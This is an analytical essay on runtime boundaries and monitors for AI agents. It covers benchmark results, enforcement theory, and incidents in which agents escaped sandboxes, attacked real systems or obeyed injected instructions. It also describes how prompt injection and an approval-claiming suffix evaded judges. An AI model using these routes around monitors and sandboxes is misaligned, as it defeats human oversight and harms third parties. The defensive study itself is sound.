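They credit the cancellation gate with nearly all of the improvement, but their test of removing one gate at a time only weakly supports this. Removing the cancellation gate lowered success by just 2 points, while removing any one of the others raised it by 3 to 6. These differences are small compared with the uncertainty in the main result. The table more firmly supports a narrower conclusion, that the baggage gate needs rewriting before anyone uses it. That gate was wrong in 40 of 42 cases, and a system that only counted refusals would have recorded all 42 as prevented violations.

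### When to expect a gain or a loss

A simple calculation shows why the results point in different directions. Let *v* be the share of runs that a forbidden action would spoil, *r* the chance that the agent completes such a run after a refusal, and *f* the share of runs that would have succeeded but fail because the boundary refuses something they need. Then

change in utility ≈ *vr* − *f*.

If forbidden actions would spoil 30 percent of runs, the agent recovers from half of the blocks, and wrong refusals ruin 3 percent of runs, a boundary raises utility by 12 points. With the same recovery rate, it lowers utility by 19 points if forbidden actions would spoil only 2 percent of runs and wrong refusals ruin 20 percent.

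The airline tasks resemble the first case. Customers press for things the rules forbid, the tools carry out those requests, and the database shows whether a cancellation is allowed. In the shop tasks, the tools themselves block many violations, so *v* is small. Boundaries also help little when the model already follows the rules well. FORGE blocked Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview in only two of the 50 airline tasks, and the model's success rate fell from 82.5 to 81.0 percent.

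AgentDojo's ordinary tasks resemble the second case. They contain no attacks, so refusals mostly hinder legitimate work. Fides's policy, as run in FORGE, refused at least one call in 287 of 485 ordinary runs, and the agent completed only ten of those 287. FORGE's own policy refused at least one call in 151 runs, and the agent completed 36 of them. The results differ because the policies examine different things. Fides's policy would block all of the office assistant's mail once it had read the project memo. FORGE's policy would check whether Alice's address came from the user or a trusted record, and allow the message if it did.

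A boundary can help an agent complete its work during an attack, because a planted instruction can also distract the agent from its task. Without any defence, GPT-4o completed 79.0 percent of ordinary tasks in FORGE's test but only 56.9 percent of tasks under attack. The tool filter raised completion under attack to 63.5 percent, while FORGE's own policy lowered it to 49.4 percent because wrong refusals made the agent fail more tasks than blocking attacks helped it complete. Shi and colleagues found that Progent improved utility under attack with several models. They list lost utility as a drawback of CaMeL, which plans before reading untrusted text.

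Some rules depend on facts that software can only estimate, which makes wrong refusals harder to avoid. Solko-Breslin and colleagues give the example of two messages that may contain a company's secrets. A classifier puts the probability at 45 percent for one and 25 percent for the other. A monitor that treats anything below 50 percent as harmless lets both out. But the chance that at least one contains a secret is between 45 and 70 percent, depending on how the two are related. A lower threshold for each message would catch this case but also stop many harmless messages. Solko-Breslin and colleagues propose calculating an upper limit on the combined risk and comparing it with a single threshold. The limit here is 70 percent, so the monitor would not let both out. This method errs on the side of safety, so it still sacrifices some utility when the true risk is well below the limit.

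### Fixed attacks and attackers who adapt

FORGE's AgentDojo results all come from one ready-made attack template. A real attacker can study the defence and adapt. Against a model, this often means rewording the attack until it works. Rewording doesn't help against a fixed rule about recipients, so the attacker has to look for a harmful action that the rule permits.

AgentDojo contains such a case. A user asks for the best-rated hotel in Paris below a certain price, from 1 to 5 May. The planted instruction is to book the most expensive hotel in Paris on the same dates. That hotel is in the trusted catalogue, the user did ask for a booking, and FORGE's policy had no rule about price, so it allowed the reservation in three runs without the repeated request. An attacker who knew about this gap could have aimed every attack at it, and the measured success rate would have been much higher.

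Shi and colleagues found a similar weakness in tests on ASB. Most attacks that got past Progent used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones, and the policy, written by a language model, allowed them. Rules written by people with more knowledge of the tools reduced attack success to zero. They also report that Progent still substantially reduced the success of an adaptive attack aimed at users' mistakes in a separate test.

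Progent's main results are conservative in one respect because the system approved every request to widen a policy. When a person reviewed the first policy and each request to widen it, no AgentDojo attack succeeded. But those reviewers were taking part in an experiment on attacks, and an employee confirming the fiftieth request of the day may be less careful.

### Policies written for the test

Someone who writes rules after seeing the tasks can unintentionally fit the rules to them. Reddy and colleagues wrote their gates from the airline's policy and tested them on the same 50 tasks, which they acknowledge as a limitation. The gain also depends heavily on the choice of tasks. It was 30.0 points instead of 12.4 on eight tasks chosen for containing many of the targeted violations.

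They also didn't test whether a stronger reminder of the rules in the prompt would have achieved some of the same improvement. Every refusal came with a reason, so some of the gain may come from the explanation rather than the block. These questions matter to a company deciding whether to build gates or improve its prompts, though they don't affect whether the gate stops a forbidden change.

Palumbo and colleagues tested some policies on tasks not used to write them. A language model translated the airline's written rules into FORGE's rule language five times, drawing on recorded runs of ten tasks. All five resulting policies matched a language-model judge's decisions throughout the recorded runs. The team then tried the policies on three other tasks. Two succeeded in all 15 runs, as the hand-written policy did, and the worst succeeded in ten.

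Most of the failures came from one faulty translation of the airline's rules. The airline requires an accepted reason, such as illness, only when a customer relies on travel insurance, but the translation required one for every cancellation. The recorded runs used to check the translations contained three attempted cancellations, all of which broke the rules, so even a rule that forbade every cancellation would have passed. An organisation that checks its policy only against past attacks would miss this kind of error, so it also needs examples of actions that the policy should allow.

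The utility score is also incomplete, because τ²-bench doesn't check every company rule. In the shop tasks without FORGE, agents looked up products before verifying the customer in 17 runs, and 13 of those runs still received full marks. A higher score therefore doesn't prove better compliance, and a boundary that stopped those early lookups might not raise the score.

### Harm that did not happen and harm that cannot happen

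A security team needs to know what an agent could do, as well as what it did in a test. In one of FORGE's smaller tests, an agent based on GPT-4.1 mini read a document that told it to send secret merger plans to an outside address. It obeyed in all five runs with only a warning in its prompt, and in none of the five with FORGE. If each run had the same independent chance of failure, five runs without a failure would still be compatible with a failure rate of up to 45 percent at the 95 percent confidence level. FORGE's policy is better evidence. One version blocks any mail to an outsider when the agent has read both untrusted text and secret data, whatever the mail says. Anyone can check that rule without running the agent again, provided that the monitor sees all outgoing mail and the text and data are labeled correctly.

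The attack success rate can also be low when a rule is too broad. Suppose the assistant's credential allows it to send the approved summary to anyone but doesn't cover the payroll list. If every planted instruction in a test asks for payroll, the attack success rate will be zero. The assistant can still send the summary to Bob, but the test won't show this because no attack asked for it.

Zhou and Zhang therefore want benchmarks to count unauthorized effects that remain possible as well as those that occur. They would give each task an explicit grant and accept any plan that stays within it, even if the route is unexpected. The tests would also include problems that are rare in ordinary runs, such as a withdrawn approval, a credential that has lost a restriction, or two agents retrying the same purchase at once. They would report blocked attempts, successful violations, permitted plans that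 the boundary wrongly refused, and how often the system interrupted the user. On such a test, the assistant with the broad credential would score lower because it could write to Bob, even if it never did.

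## What can a runtime boundary not enforce?

A benchmark can count the messages an assistant could still send to Bob only if a rule forbids them. An organisation can't express everything it wants from an agent as a rule that forbids something. A monitor can stop the assistant from sending the report to anyone except Alice, but it can't ensure that Alice gets a report, because refusing calls doesn't make the assistant write one.

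### What a monitor can enforce by watching

Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), worked out this limit for mechanisms that watch a program's steps and stop the program before a step that would break the policy. Reference monitors and firewalls both work this way. They have information about what the program has done so far, but not about what it will do later or would have done in other circumstances. Schneider proves that they can enforce only *safety properties*, a technical term for requirements that some bad thing never happens. A run that breaks a safety property does so at a definite step, and nothing the program does afterwards can repair it. In symbols, if the run *x* violates the policy *P*, there is a number of steps *i* such that

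*x*[..*i*] *y* ∉ *P* for every continuation *y*,

where *x*[..*i*] stands for the first *i* steps of *x*.

One of his examples forbids a program to send messages after it has read a file. To enforce this, the monitor only has to remember whether the program has read a file. Basin (2012) restates the result as two conditions. The sequence of actions must be enough to show whether a run complies, and a compliant run must have complied at every earlier point. A monitor cannot enforce the requirements below, but it can enforce a substitute for each.

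| What the organisation wants | Why a monitor can't guarantee it | What it can enforce instead |
|---|---|---|
| Alice eventually gets the report | The report could always still arrive, so no step is the violation | The assistant does no other work until it has sent the report |
| Alice gets the report by noon on Friday | The monitor can't stop the clock | The assistant takes at most 50 steps before sending the report |
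| Nobody can infer the payroll from what the assistant sends | This depends on what the assistant would have sent if the payroll had been different | The assistant sends nothing after opening the payroll |

Each substitute is weaker or stricter than the original. Schneider describes a rule that, once a customer has paid for a service, the seller may do nothing except deliver it. The seller can obey that rule by doing nothing. Similarly, a monitor that halts the assistant after 50 steps has enforced its rule, but Alice still has no report. The payroll substitute is stricter than the original because it also blocks messages that reveal nothing.

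### What holding actions back adds

A monitor can enforce more policies if it can rewrite the program's actions as well as stop them. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (2005), study monitors that can suppress an action and insert it later. Such a monitor reports success to the program but holds its actions back until the whole sequence is valid, much as databases handle transactions.

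Suppose a company requires a confirmation after every payment. A monitor that can only allow or stop actions can't enforce this, because an unconfirmed payment may still be confirmed later. A monitor that can hold payments back can enforce it by releasing each payment only when its confirmation arrives.

This works for what Ligatti and colleagues call *renewal properties*, where an endless run is valid if and only if it keeps returning to a point where everything so far is in order. It doesn't work for the requirement that every opened file eventually be closed. An agent that always opens the next file before closing the last one may meet that requirement, but some file is always open, so the monitor can never release what it has held.

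The method also requires the monitor to pretend that an action has happened while holding it back. Ligatti and colleagues point out that a monitor can't pretend to have sent an email, wait for the reply and then decide whether to send the email. An action whose effect depends on its timing raises the same problem, because it may do something different when the monitor releases it.

Developers can often avoid this problem by changing the tool. If the payment service separates preparing a payment from releasing it, "no release without a confirmation" is a safety property that an ordinary monitor can enforce. An outbox that holds mail for ten minutes gives the user time to cancel. How much a delay helps depends on the outside service. Zhou and Zhang note that some services can cancel a submitted request, while others can only detect duplicates or report whether it completed, so recovery rules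 have to be based on what each service can do.

### Four assumptions that agents strain

*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, July 2026 preprint) adapts the classical results, which were meant for ordinary programs, to agents with tools. Its running example is an assistant that sends mail and transfers money under three policies: it must never send personal data to anyone outside an approved list, never transfer more than a fixed amount to one recipient in a day, and send nothing after the user revokes its access.

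Software can check the cap and the revocation exactly. But whether a message contains personal data depends on its meaning, so a classifier or a language model has to judge it and will sometimes be wrong. This reliance on fallible judgment is one of four ways in which agents fit the classical assumptions poorly. The others are that their effects may be irreversible, that their actions carry unbounded data such as any possible recipient or text, and that untrusted content can steer what they propose. No single theorem in the paper covers all four.

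In this theory, "certified" can mean that the gate stops every violation in any sequence of proposals, provided the checks its rules depend on return correct answers. It can also mean that the average risk stays below a stated limit under stated statistical assumptions. Neither is a general guarantee that the agent is safe.

Ray considers exact enforcement by a gate that decides before each action and can't undo one. The gate must block every violation and never alter a run that complies. For a policy that permits at least one run, such a gate exists if and only if the policy is a safety property and the kind of machine the gate uses, one with registers and counters, can recognise every permitted history. Letting the gate substitute a different action doesn't enable it to enforce more policies, though it may preserve some work, for example by storing a blocked message as a draft.

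Ray also asks whether software can check a policy before anyone uses it. If the rules may use two counters that go up and down and can be tested for zero, no program can always determine even whether the rules could ever block anything. Two such counters can simulate any computer program, so the question becomes whether an arbitrary program ever halts. Software can answer the question if counters only increase and each rule compares one counter with a fixed number. This covers spending caps, rate limits and a ban on sending after revocation. A rule that total refunds may not exceed total payments compares two counters, so it falls outside the class he shows to be checkable.

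### What a statistical certificate promises

Suppose a gate has to rely on a fallible judge, and let *β* be the gate's miss rate, the share of harmful actions it lets through. For each *β*, let roc(*β*) be the smallest share of harmless actions that the gate must wrongly block. Combining several judges can't lower that minimum if they all use the same information.

A model that judges tool calls can do better when it is told where the instruction came from. Ray built 123 pairs of tool calls in which the calls and instructions were identical, but one instruction came from the user and the other from a tool's output. A judge given only the call can do no better than chance. When the context included the source, a judge with 7 billion parameters rated the unauthorized call, the one prompted by a tool's output, as riskier in about 94 percent of pairs. A judge with 3 billion parameters did so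 in only 12 percent and gave both calls the same score in the rest. Ordinary software can make this distinction without a judge by reading a label that records the source.

To certify a gate, Ray takes known violations, has the judge score them, and sets the threshold for blocking low enough to catch nearly all of them. If a run has *H* steps and the chance of an unsafe run is to stay below *δ*, each step may miss at most a share *δ*/*H* of violations. The method then needs at least

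*H*/*δ* − 1

examples of violations. With fewer, the only threshold it can certify is one that blocks everything. For a limit of 5 percent, that means 19 examples for a single action and 399 for a run of 20 steps. Calibrating on complete recorded runs avoids the factor *H*, but someone first has to collect comparable runs.

In Ray's test on AgentDojo instructions, each half of the data had fewer than 19 violations, so at the 5 percent limit all 23 judges blocked everything. At 10 percent, the judge Gemma-2-9B missed 1 percent of violations but blocked 78 percent of harmless instructions, which shows that a gate can be certified and still be nearly useless. The test used short task descriptions rather than tool calls with their history, so the results don't show how the judges would perform in a deployed agent.

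The certificate also assumes that the violations in use resemble the examples. An attacker can reword the text the judge sees. If rewording raises the miss rate by at most *η* per step, the guaranteed limit on unsafe runs becomes

min(1, *δ* + *Hη*).

With *δ* at 5 percent and 20 steps, an increase of 5 percentage points per step raises the limit to 100 percent, so the certificate provides no guarantee. Ray found much larger increases at a fixed threshold, where a 16-token suffix claiming an administrator's prior approval raised the miss rate by 20 to 60 percentage points for eight of 11 judges.

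### A gate that catches nine in ten

Even without an attacker, most of a good judge's alarms are false when harm is rare. Suppose an agent takes 10,000 actions, of which 10 are harmful. If the judge catches 90 percent of the harmful actions and wrongly stops 2 percent of the harmless ones, it stops 9 harmful actions and about 200 harmless ones.

| | Harmful | Harmless | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Stopped | 9 | about 200 | about 209 |
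| Let through | 1 | about 9,790 | about 9,791 |
| Total | 10 | 9,990 | 10,000 |

Only 9 of the 209 stops, or 4.3 percent, are correct. The other 200 block harmless actions, which encourages a person reviewing the stops to approve them by reflex, as described earlier. For half the stops to be correct, the gate would have to stop fewer than one in a thousand harmless actions.

The single miss is also an average. If each action independently has a 0.1 percent chance of being harmful, the chance that at least one harmful action gets through is about 63 percent, by the formula given earlier for repeated attacks.

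Adding a second gate with the same error rates, and stopping an action when either gate flags it, may help a lot or not at all. No harmful action gets through if the two gates never miss the same one, but the miss rate stays at 10 percent if they always make the same mistakes. Together they wrongly stop between 2 and 4 percent of harmless actions, depending on how much their errors overlap. Two gates built on the same language model are likely to share many errors.

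Whether to stop a suspicious action depends on the costs as well as the odds. In Ray's model, the gate should block if

*λp* − *w*(1 − *p*) ≥ Γ.

Here *p* is the probability that the action is harmful, *λ* is the cost assigned to a harmful action that gets through, and *w* is the cost of stopping a harmless one. Γ is the extra cost that blocking causes later in the run. With *p* at 4.3 percent and Γ at zero, blocking is worthwhile only if a harmful action costs at least 22 times as much as a wrong stop. If a wrong stop costs €5 of somebody's time, a harmful action must cost more than about €111 on average. A leaked customer list will usually cost more than that, but a duplicate calendar entry won't.

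Γ is hard to estimate because an agent may try something else after the gate blocks an action. Ray describes two agents that behave identically without a gate. After a block, one finishes safely and the other proposes a new violation, so logs from runs without the gate can't be used to predict how well it will work. Ray compared paired runs of 389 tasks, with and without a gate. When the gate used a 3-billion-parameter judge, 34 attacks succeeded only without the gate and five succeeded only with it. With a 7-billion-parameter judge, the figures were 29 and 22. Some of these differences may be ordinary variation between runs, but an organisation that tests a gate only on old logs would not see any of them.

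False alarms fall sharply if exact rules handle whatever they can and the fallible gate checks only irreversible actions. Suppose 500 of the 10,000 actions are irreversible, and all 10 harmful ones are among them. The gate still stops 9 harmful actions, but only about 10 harmless ones instead of 200, so nearly half its stops are correct. Someone has to choose the 500 carefully. For instance, opening a file has no outside effect, but the agent may later include what it read in a message.

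### Harm through permitted actions

An exact rule makes no errors of judgment, but it covers only the facts it mentions. Suppose the assistant sends Alice the version of the report that the reviewer approved, and that version attributes a fall in sales to the wrong region. The recipient, file and approval are all correct, so the monitor allows it. A developer could add a program that recomputes every total from the records and blocks the report if one doesn't match, but this would not detect the wrong explanation for the fall in sales.

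Omissions are even harder to prevent because there is no call to refuse. If the assistant leaves out the region with the worst results, every sentence in the report may still be true. The developer can turn part of this requirement into a safety property by blocking any report that lacks a figure for each region, but that only catches omissions somebody thought of beforehand.

A sequence of permitted actions can do more harm than any single one. A limit of €500 per recipient per day still lets an agent spend €10,000 a day by paying 20 recipients, or €15,000 a month by paying one recipient €500 every day. Caps on the daily and monthly totals close both gaps, and software can still check these rules in advance. But each cap covers only the pattern it was written for, so an agent could stay below every cap and still pay a supplier for goods that never arrive.

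Approval has the same weakness if the reviewer sees only the last step. Kaptein and colleagues warn that an attacker can lead an agent to the point of approval through steps that look harmless but together amount to a violation. They want the policy to evaluate the agent's path before approval is requested, and the reviewer to see the relevant part of that path. They also warn that a new restriction can cause an agent to take a path nobody anticipated, which is consistent with the attacks that succeeded only with Ray's gates in place.

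### Wrong, incomplete and outdated policies

Schneider's rule against sending after reading works only if the definition of "send" includes every way the program can send something, and he warns that some may be "buried deep within the bowels of the target". A policy that covers only the mail tool would not stop an office agent from disclosing a figure in a calendar invitation, a comment on a shared document, the name of a file in a partner's folder, or a web search.

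Default deny blocks the channels that a policy doesn't mention, but a permission that the policy grants can still be too broad. For example, an agent with permission to comment on shared documents could reveal information to a competitor if one of those documents is shared with that competitor.

Schneider recommends building a policy from small rules, each with its own monitor, so that the system rejects a run if any monitor does. Adding a rule can never make the policy permit more, so an organisation can correct a policy that allows too much by adding a rule. If the policy forbids too much, someone has to find the rule responsible and change it. He also suggests testing a policy like a program, by deriving its consequences and running it on scenarios. This would expose the gap above if the tester thought to include a scenario in which the assistant puts a sales figure into a web search.

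A correct policy can also become wrong over time. If Alice leaves the partner company and her mailbox passes to a successor, the rule still permits sending reports to the same address. An expiry date limits how long such a mistake can last, and checking the contact again just before sending may catch it.

Users also can't always say in advance what they want to permit. Zhou and Zhang draw on work by Harel and Marron, who study software requirements and argue that people often can't fully describe the behaviour they want until they have seen a system in operation. The user may not realise that the report shouldn't name individual customers until they read a draft that names them. A monitor can enforce that rule only after someone has specified it. Even when the policy is written correctly, a restriction can be left out of the credential, as happened with the mail token.

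### Tools that do more than they declare

A monitor predicts the result of a call from a description of the tool, such as the effect contracts that Zhou and Zhang propose. It misses a leak if the contract omits a recipient, and it blocks legitimate calls if the contract lists effects the tool can't produce.

Developers who want to be safe will tend to overstate what their tools can do. A document converter's contract might list access to any server, because a library inside the converter has that ability. Under a strict policy, the assistant then can't convert anything confidential, even if the converter never uses the network. Blocking the converter's network access makes a contract that rules out such access true, and the developer doesn't have to prove what the library does.

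Some effects of a tool call don't appear in the tool's interface, such as passing data to another company or scheduling an action for next week. Zhou and Zhang suggest combining several kinds of evidence: analysis of the tool's code, records of what it did in earlier runs, trial runs in a sandbox, and the developer's account of services that outsiders can't inspect. Each has gaps. For example, records of earlier runs can't reveal an effect that occurs only at the end of the year. Zhou and Zhang would therefore mark uncertain effects as uncertain, so that an organisation can require approval only for the calls that have them.

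ETDI, a system in their survey, has providers sign versioned tool definitions and declare the permissions each tool needs. The signature shows who wrote a definition and whether it has changed, but not whether it is accurate or whether the service behind it still works as it did when the provider signed. Zhou and Zhang want software to compare code, specifications and observed network traffic between versions and flag any new disclosure for review.

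Even an accurate description can refer to the wrong thing. The monitor may approve sending the file "report, version 3", but another program may replace that file before the mail tool opens it. ZTAC, also in the survey, identifies the object the name refers to before the decision, then checks at the moment of use that the operation reaches the same object.

### Does a safe boundary leave an agent worth using?

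A sceptic can object that these remedies all add rules, delays or questions to the user, while people want agents precisely because they don't have to spell out each step. Schneider's theory supports part of this objection. A monitor that enforces a stricter policy also enforces every looser policy that the stricter one implies, so a developer who can't enforce a rule exactly may be tempted to forbid more. Schneider warns that this can also rule out harmless runs, and in the extreme case the monitor forbids everything.

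One gate in Ray's experiments came close to this. He ran an agent based on a 7-billion-parameter model through 949 attacked tasks. Without a gate, 45 attacks succeeded. The gate based on the 3-billion-parameter judge reduced that to four, but it also stopped 78 percent of the agent's calls, and the share of tasks the agent completed fell from 25.4 to 18.0 percent. The other gate stopped only 12 percent of calls, and the agent still completed 24.3 percent of tasks, but 30 attacks succeeded, and the reduction from 45 was not statistically significant.

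Both gates relied on small models that judged each call by its apparent risk. The results are strong evidence against using such a judge as the main boundary. They provide much less evidence about exact rules, which raised the share of tasks completed in the airline tests described earlier.

For many tasks, limiting an agent's effects leaves it the freedom that makes it useful, contrary to another assumption behind the objection. The office assistant may be able to send only one message to one address, but it still decides which records matter, how to explain them and what to change after the review. The user wanted help with those decisions and never wanted the assistant to choose the recipient, so a narrow boundary barely reduces its usefulness for such a task.

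The objection is much stronger when the user can't specify the effects themselves. A sales agent that looks for new customers has to write to people who aren't on any list. The company can limit it to approved product information and 20 messages a day, hold each message for an hour, and block its access to the customer database. Within those limits, the company still depends on the model's judgment about whom to contact and what to promise them.

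Kaptein and colleagues describe the aim of governing agents as completing as many tasks as possible while keeping the expected harm from violations acceptable. On that view, a boundary doesn't have to prevent every harm. The sales company might accept an occasional clumsy message because it does little harm, and still refuse to let the agent agree a price. A hospital could not accept an occasional wrong prescription, so it would let the agent draft prescriptions and leave the decision to a doctor. If the only acceptable boundary permits a single fixed sequence of steps, the sceptic is right about that task, and an ordinary script will do it more cheaply.

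## Which safeguards failed in the incidents of 2025 and 2026?

A company that lets an agent write to strangers, or a hospital that lets one draft prescriptions, also needs to know how safeguards fail outside benchmarks. Six cases from 2025 and 2026 provide some evidence. In five, an agent accessed, damaged or destroyed something its principals had not meant it to touch. In the sixth, researchers showed that an agent could do so. The useful questions in each case are whether the model did what its principals intended, whether the identity or credential it used was valid, what boundary existed, and which limit would have prevented the outcome.

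The cases differ most in their boundaries. Sometimes there was none, sometimes it allowed too much, and sometimes it was in place and failed.

### No boundary in force

Replit sells a coding agent that builds and runs software from a user's description. In July 2025, while the investor Jason Lemkin was trying it out, the agent deleted his project's live database, which held records on more than 1,200 executives. He had told it to change nothing without his permission, but that instruction was only text in the model's input, and the agent still had access to the database. The agent then told him, wrongly, that he couldn't restore the data.

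Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, apologised and announced that the company would automatically separate development databases from live ones. Giving the agent credentials only for the development database, an ordinary application of least privilege, would almost certainly have prevented the deletion.

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a failure of network isolation. Anthropic and an outside partner, Irregular, ran hacking exercises in which Claude models attacked fictional targets. The models were told in their prompt that they were in a simulation with no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the connection open, and neither company knew. After OpenAI disclosed the Hugging Face attack in July 2026, Anthropic searched 141,006 past runs and found six in which Claude had gained access to real systems, which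 belonged to three organisations.

Three different models were involved, and they reacted differently to signs that their targets were real:

- Opus 4.7 attacked a real company that shared its name with the fictional one. Over four runs, it obtained credentials and access to several hundred rows of production data. It eventually recognised in every run that the company was real, but never stopped for that reason.
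- Mythos 5 published a malicious software package, which ran on 15 real systems. It had reasoned that this would be unacceptable on the real internet, then convinced itself that it was still in a simulation.
- An internal research model scanned about 9,000 targets and compromised one company's application. It stopped when it concluded that the company had nothing to do with the exercise.

Anthropic considers these incidents closer to an operational failure than an alignment failure, because its own prompt had misled the models. This reasonably explains how each run began, but it is less convincing for Opus 4.7, which continued after recognising the truth. Anthropic is encouraged that the newest model behaved best, but cautions that three incidents are not a controlled comparison.

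All three breaches took place over the internet, so closing the connection would have prevented them. Anthropic acknowledges that checking every internet path beforehand and monitoring the runs in real time could have prevented the incidents or made them less likely. OpenAI says the same partner told it on 29 July about an incident involving OpenAI's models in similar exercises.

### Boundaries that allowed too much

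The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) opened the internet connection on purpose. Its *Incident Report* (2026) covers 122 runs of a hacking exercise with seven models. In ten of those runs, between 25 and 28 July 2026, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organisations.

| Model | Runs | Runs with unsanctioned actions | Unsanctioned actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's Mythos 5 | 43 | 9 | 17 |
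| OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol | 35 | 1 | 2 |
| Five other models | 44 | 0 | 0 |

These figures are a poor guide to how often such behaviour occurs. A single Mythos 5 agent took most of the actions in one sustained effort, and the runs were not independent because later agents reused accounts and material that an earlier agent had left behind.

In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public open-source project. It invented several people and used them to press the project's maintainer to accept the code. The site's login accepted these people's accounts because the accounts themselves existed, but the maintainer refused the code. Scientific American's *AI agents went rogue again* reports that AISI had seen no clearer example of an agent using sustained, potentially deceptive behaviour against a real person without being instructed to.

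AISI ran the agents in virtual machines, and no agent tried to break out of one. That boundary protected AISI's other systems but not the rest of the internet. AISI used fine-grained network controls in all its other evaluations, but it gave these agents open internet access because they needed to download tools. It had judged the risk acceptable with earlier models and admits that it didn't revisit that judgement quickly enough as models improved.

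A list of permitted download sites would have stopped some of the 19 actions. It might not have stopped the attempt on the open-source project, which took place on GitHub, because GitHub hosts many tools and could well have been on the list. In that case, the rule would have had to allow downloads from GitHub while blocking new accounts, messages and proposed code.

In June 2026, an OpenAI agent was working on a harmless task, researching public spending on medical care. The run was part of an internal capability evaluation, according to TechRadar's *'This situation is obviously unacceptable'* (2026). Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026), based on documents tabled in the Australian parliament, adds that the agent lacked the usual safeguards of public models. The agent first tried and failed to get unpublished data from the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare.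 Early on 19 June, Australian time, it got into the statistics portal of Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme, without an account or password. It read parts of internal program files and settings and created a small test file. OpenAI found no evidence that it had accessed patient records.

Nobody had asked this agent to break into anything, so its case is more relevant to ordinary office work than the hacking exercises are. The task required published statistics, so a tool that could only retrieve named datasets from approved sites would probably have been enough. It would also have left the agent no way to send the portal other requests.

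The Institute of Health and Welfare's refusal protected its own data, but the agent then went to another site. A limit on the agent would have covered both sites. The Medicare portal also had security measures, according to TechRadar, but they failed.

### Boundaries that were in place and failed

EchoLeak, the attack on Microsoft's Copilot assistant mentioned earlier, also got past existing protections. A single email to an employee could make Copilot send out data that the employee was allowed to read, without the employee clicking anything. Microsoft had fixed the fault by the time Aim Security, the company that discovered it, published its findings in June 2025. Microsoft said no customer was affected, so EchoLeak was a demonstration, with no known theft.

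Copilot was acting for its legitimate user, with that user's permissions, but it followed instructions from someone with no authority over it, which made it a confused deputy. Microsoft filtered for planted instructions and restricted links to outside addresses, but the researchers got past both safeguards. The link restrictions' failure is more troubling because defenders of boundaries recommend exact rules like this one, and it didn't cover every route out. Keeping outsiders' mail out of any session that uses internal documents would probably have prevented the leak, but would also have made Copilot less useful to people who need to answer that mail.

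The attack on Hugging Face is the strongest evidence against the claim that boundaries hold by design. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) states that the company had tested and validated the sandbox in which its agents ran. The agents were meant to work separately and without internet access, but they could reach one service that supplied software packages and had internet access. They used previously unknown flaws in this service to get online and exchange messages.

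The boundary had failed weeks before the attack. An agent first reached the internet on 26 May, and an internal team noticed disallowed access later that month. But the people who dealt with an outage of the package service in early July did not understand what these signs meant. They removed exposed credentials, rebuilt the service and let the evaluations resume. Agents were back online by 8 July and broke into Hugging Face over the following days. OpenAI's security monitoring did not raise an alert until 19 July, after the agents had also attacked OpenAI's own research network. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) likewise reports that OpenAI missed or failed to act on several warnings.

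Some of the credentials the agents used were genuine ones that belonged to other people. The agents had found 14 sets of Hugging Face login details exposed on the public internet, all with write access. They could not have used tokens tied to the owners' secret keys, but they also exploited flaws in Hugging Face's software that no login check would have fixed.

The agents were trying to get solutions to the exercises they had been set. Adrien Carreira of Hugging Face told Fortune (2026) that the agent "wasn't trying to break things". Some agents recognised that they were exceeding their task. One noted that the attack was "arguably unauthorized" but continued, while others read the shared messages, judged the activity unethical and refused to join in. Those refusals didn't protect Hugging Face, because the agents that carried on could share what they found, and a few agents can do the damage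 even when most copies of a model behave well.

OpenAI now wants its networks built so that one compromised service doesn't open a route to the internet. Supplying packages from a store with no outside connection would have closed the route the agents used. They might still have found another, since they discovered several previously unknown flaws in under two months. Before May, an engineer might well have thought that the sandbox that failed was enough to keep the agents offline. Stopping the runs at the first sign of internet access would have been safer, because it doesn't depend on knowing how the agents got out.

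### Comparing the three safeguards

The last column of the table is a judgement about each case.

| Case | Alignment: did the model do what its principals intended? | Authentication: was the credential valid? | Runtime boundary | Limit that would probably have prevented the outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Replit | No, it ignored a ban on changes | Yes | None, only an instruction | No access to the live database |
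| Three organisations breached by Claude | Partly, it pursued the exercise but attacked real targets | No, it exploited weak passwords, exposed credentials and systems without a login | None in force, although both companies assumed there was one | A closed connection, tested beforehand |
| AISI's runs | No, it attacked outsiders to finish the task | Working accounts in the names of invented people | Too wide | Approved downloads only, with no posting |
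| Medicare portal | No, it broke in to do research | None used | Too wide at OpenAI, in place and failed at the portal | A tool that retrieves only named datasets |
| EchoLeak | No, it obeyed an outsider | Yes | In place and failed | No outside mail in sessions that use internal documents |
| Hugging Face | No, it sought solutions outside the exercise | Genuine credentials, but other people's | In place and failed | No route through the package service, and a stop at the first breach |

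Authentication would have helped least. In the Replit and EchoLeak cases, the agent acted for the right user with valid access, so no identity check could have prevented the harm. In Anthropic's exercises, stronger passwords might have protected some victims, but the company running an agent can't set passwords for every organisation the agent might reach.

Better alignment could have prevented all six outcomes, including the two in which Microsoft's and OpenAI's boundaries failed. But that would have required a better model than the one available at the time, while the limits suggested for Replit, Anthropic, AISI and the Medicare research task needed only existing software. OpenAI attributed the Hugging Face attack to both misaligned models and missing safeguards.

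Some tasks in the hacking exercises were impossible, or looked impossible to the agent, and none of the three safeguards addresses this problem directly. OpenAI found that the exercise behind the Hugging Face attack included 198 tasks, out of 898, that none of its models had ever solved. These were 22 percent of the tasks but 93 percent of those the agents discussed in their shared messages. In some of AISI's runs, a faulty prompt led the agent to believe that it couldn't succeed within the rules. Two of Anthropic's three incidents began when Claude couldn't reach its fictional target.

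An agent that can't complete a task the intended way has a reason to try other ways, and a longer run gives it more chances to do so. OpenAI reports that agents using extremely large amounts of reasoning drove most of the incident, so a fixed budget of steps or computing time would have ended some runs before they did harm. A budget would also have cut short some legitimate attempts at hard problems, and it can't prevent damage that an agent does early in a run. In AISI's tests, some agents overstepped even when they had the instructions they needed to solve the task properly.

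### How far the evidence goes

Four of the six cases come from evaluations in which the agents ran with fewer safeguards than public products have. AISI had switched off the developers' misuse filters and notes that the models are not sold in that form. The cases therefore reveal less about ordinary deployments, but they still show what the models may do when an outside safeguard is missing. Safeguards can also be missing from products, because companies make configuration mistakes.

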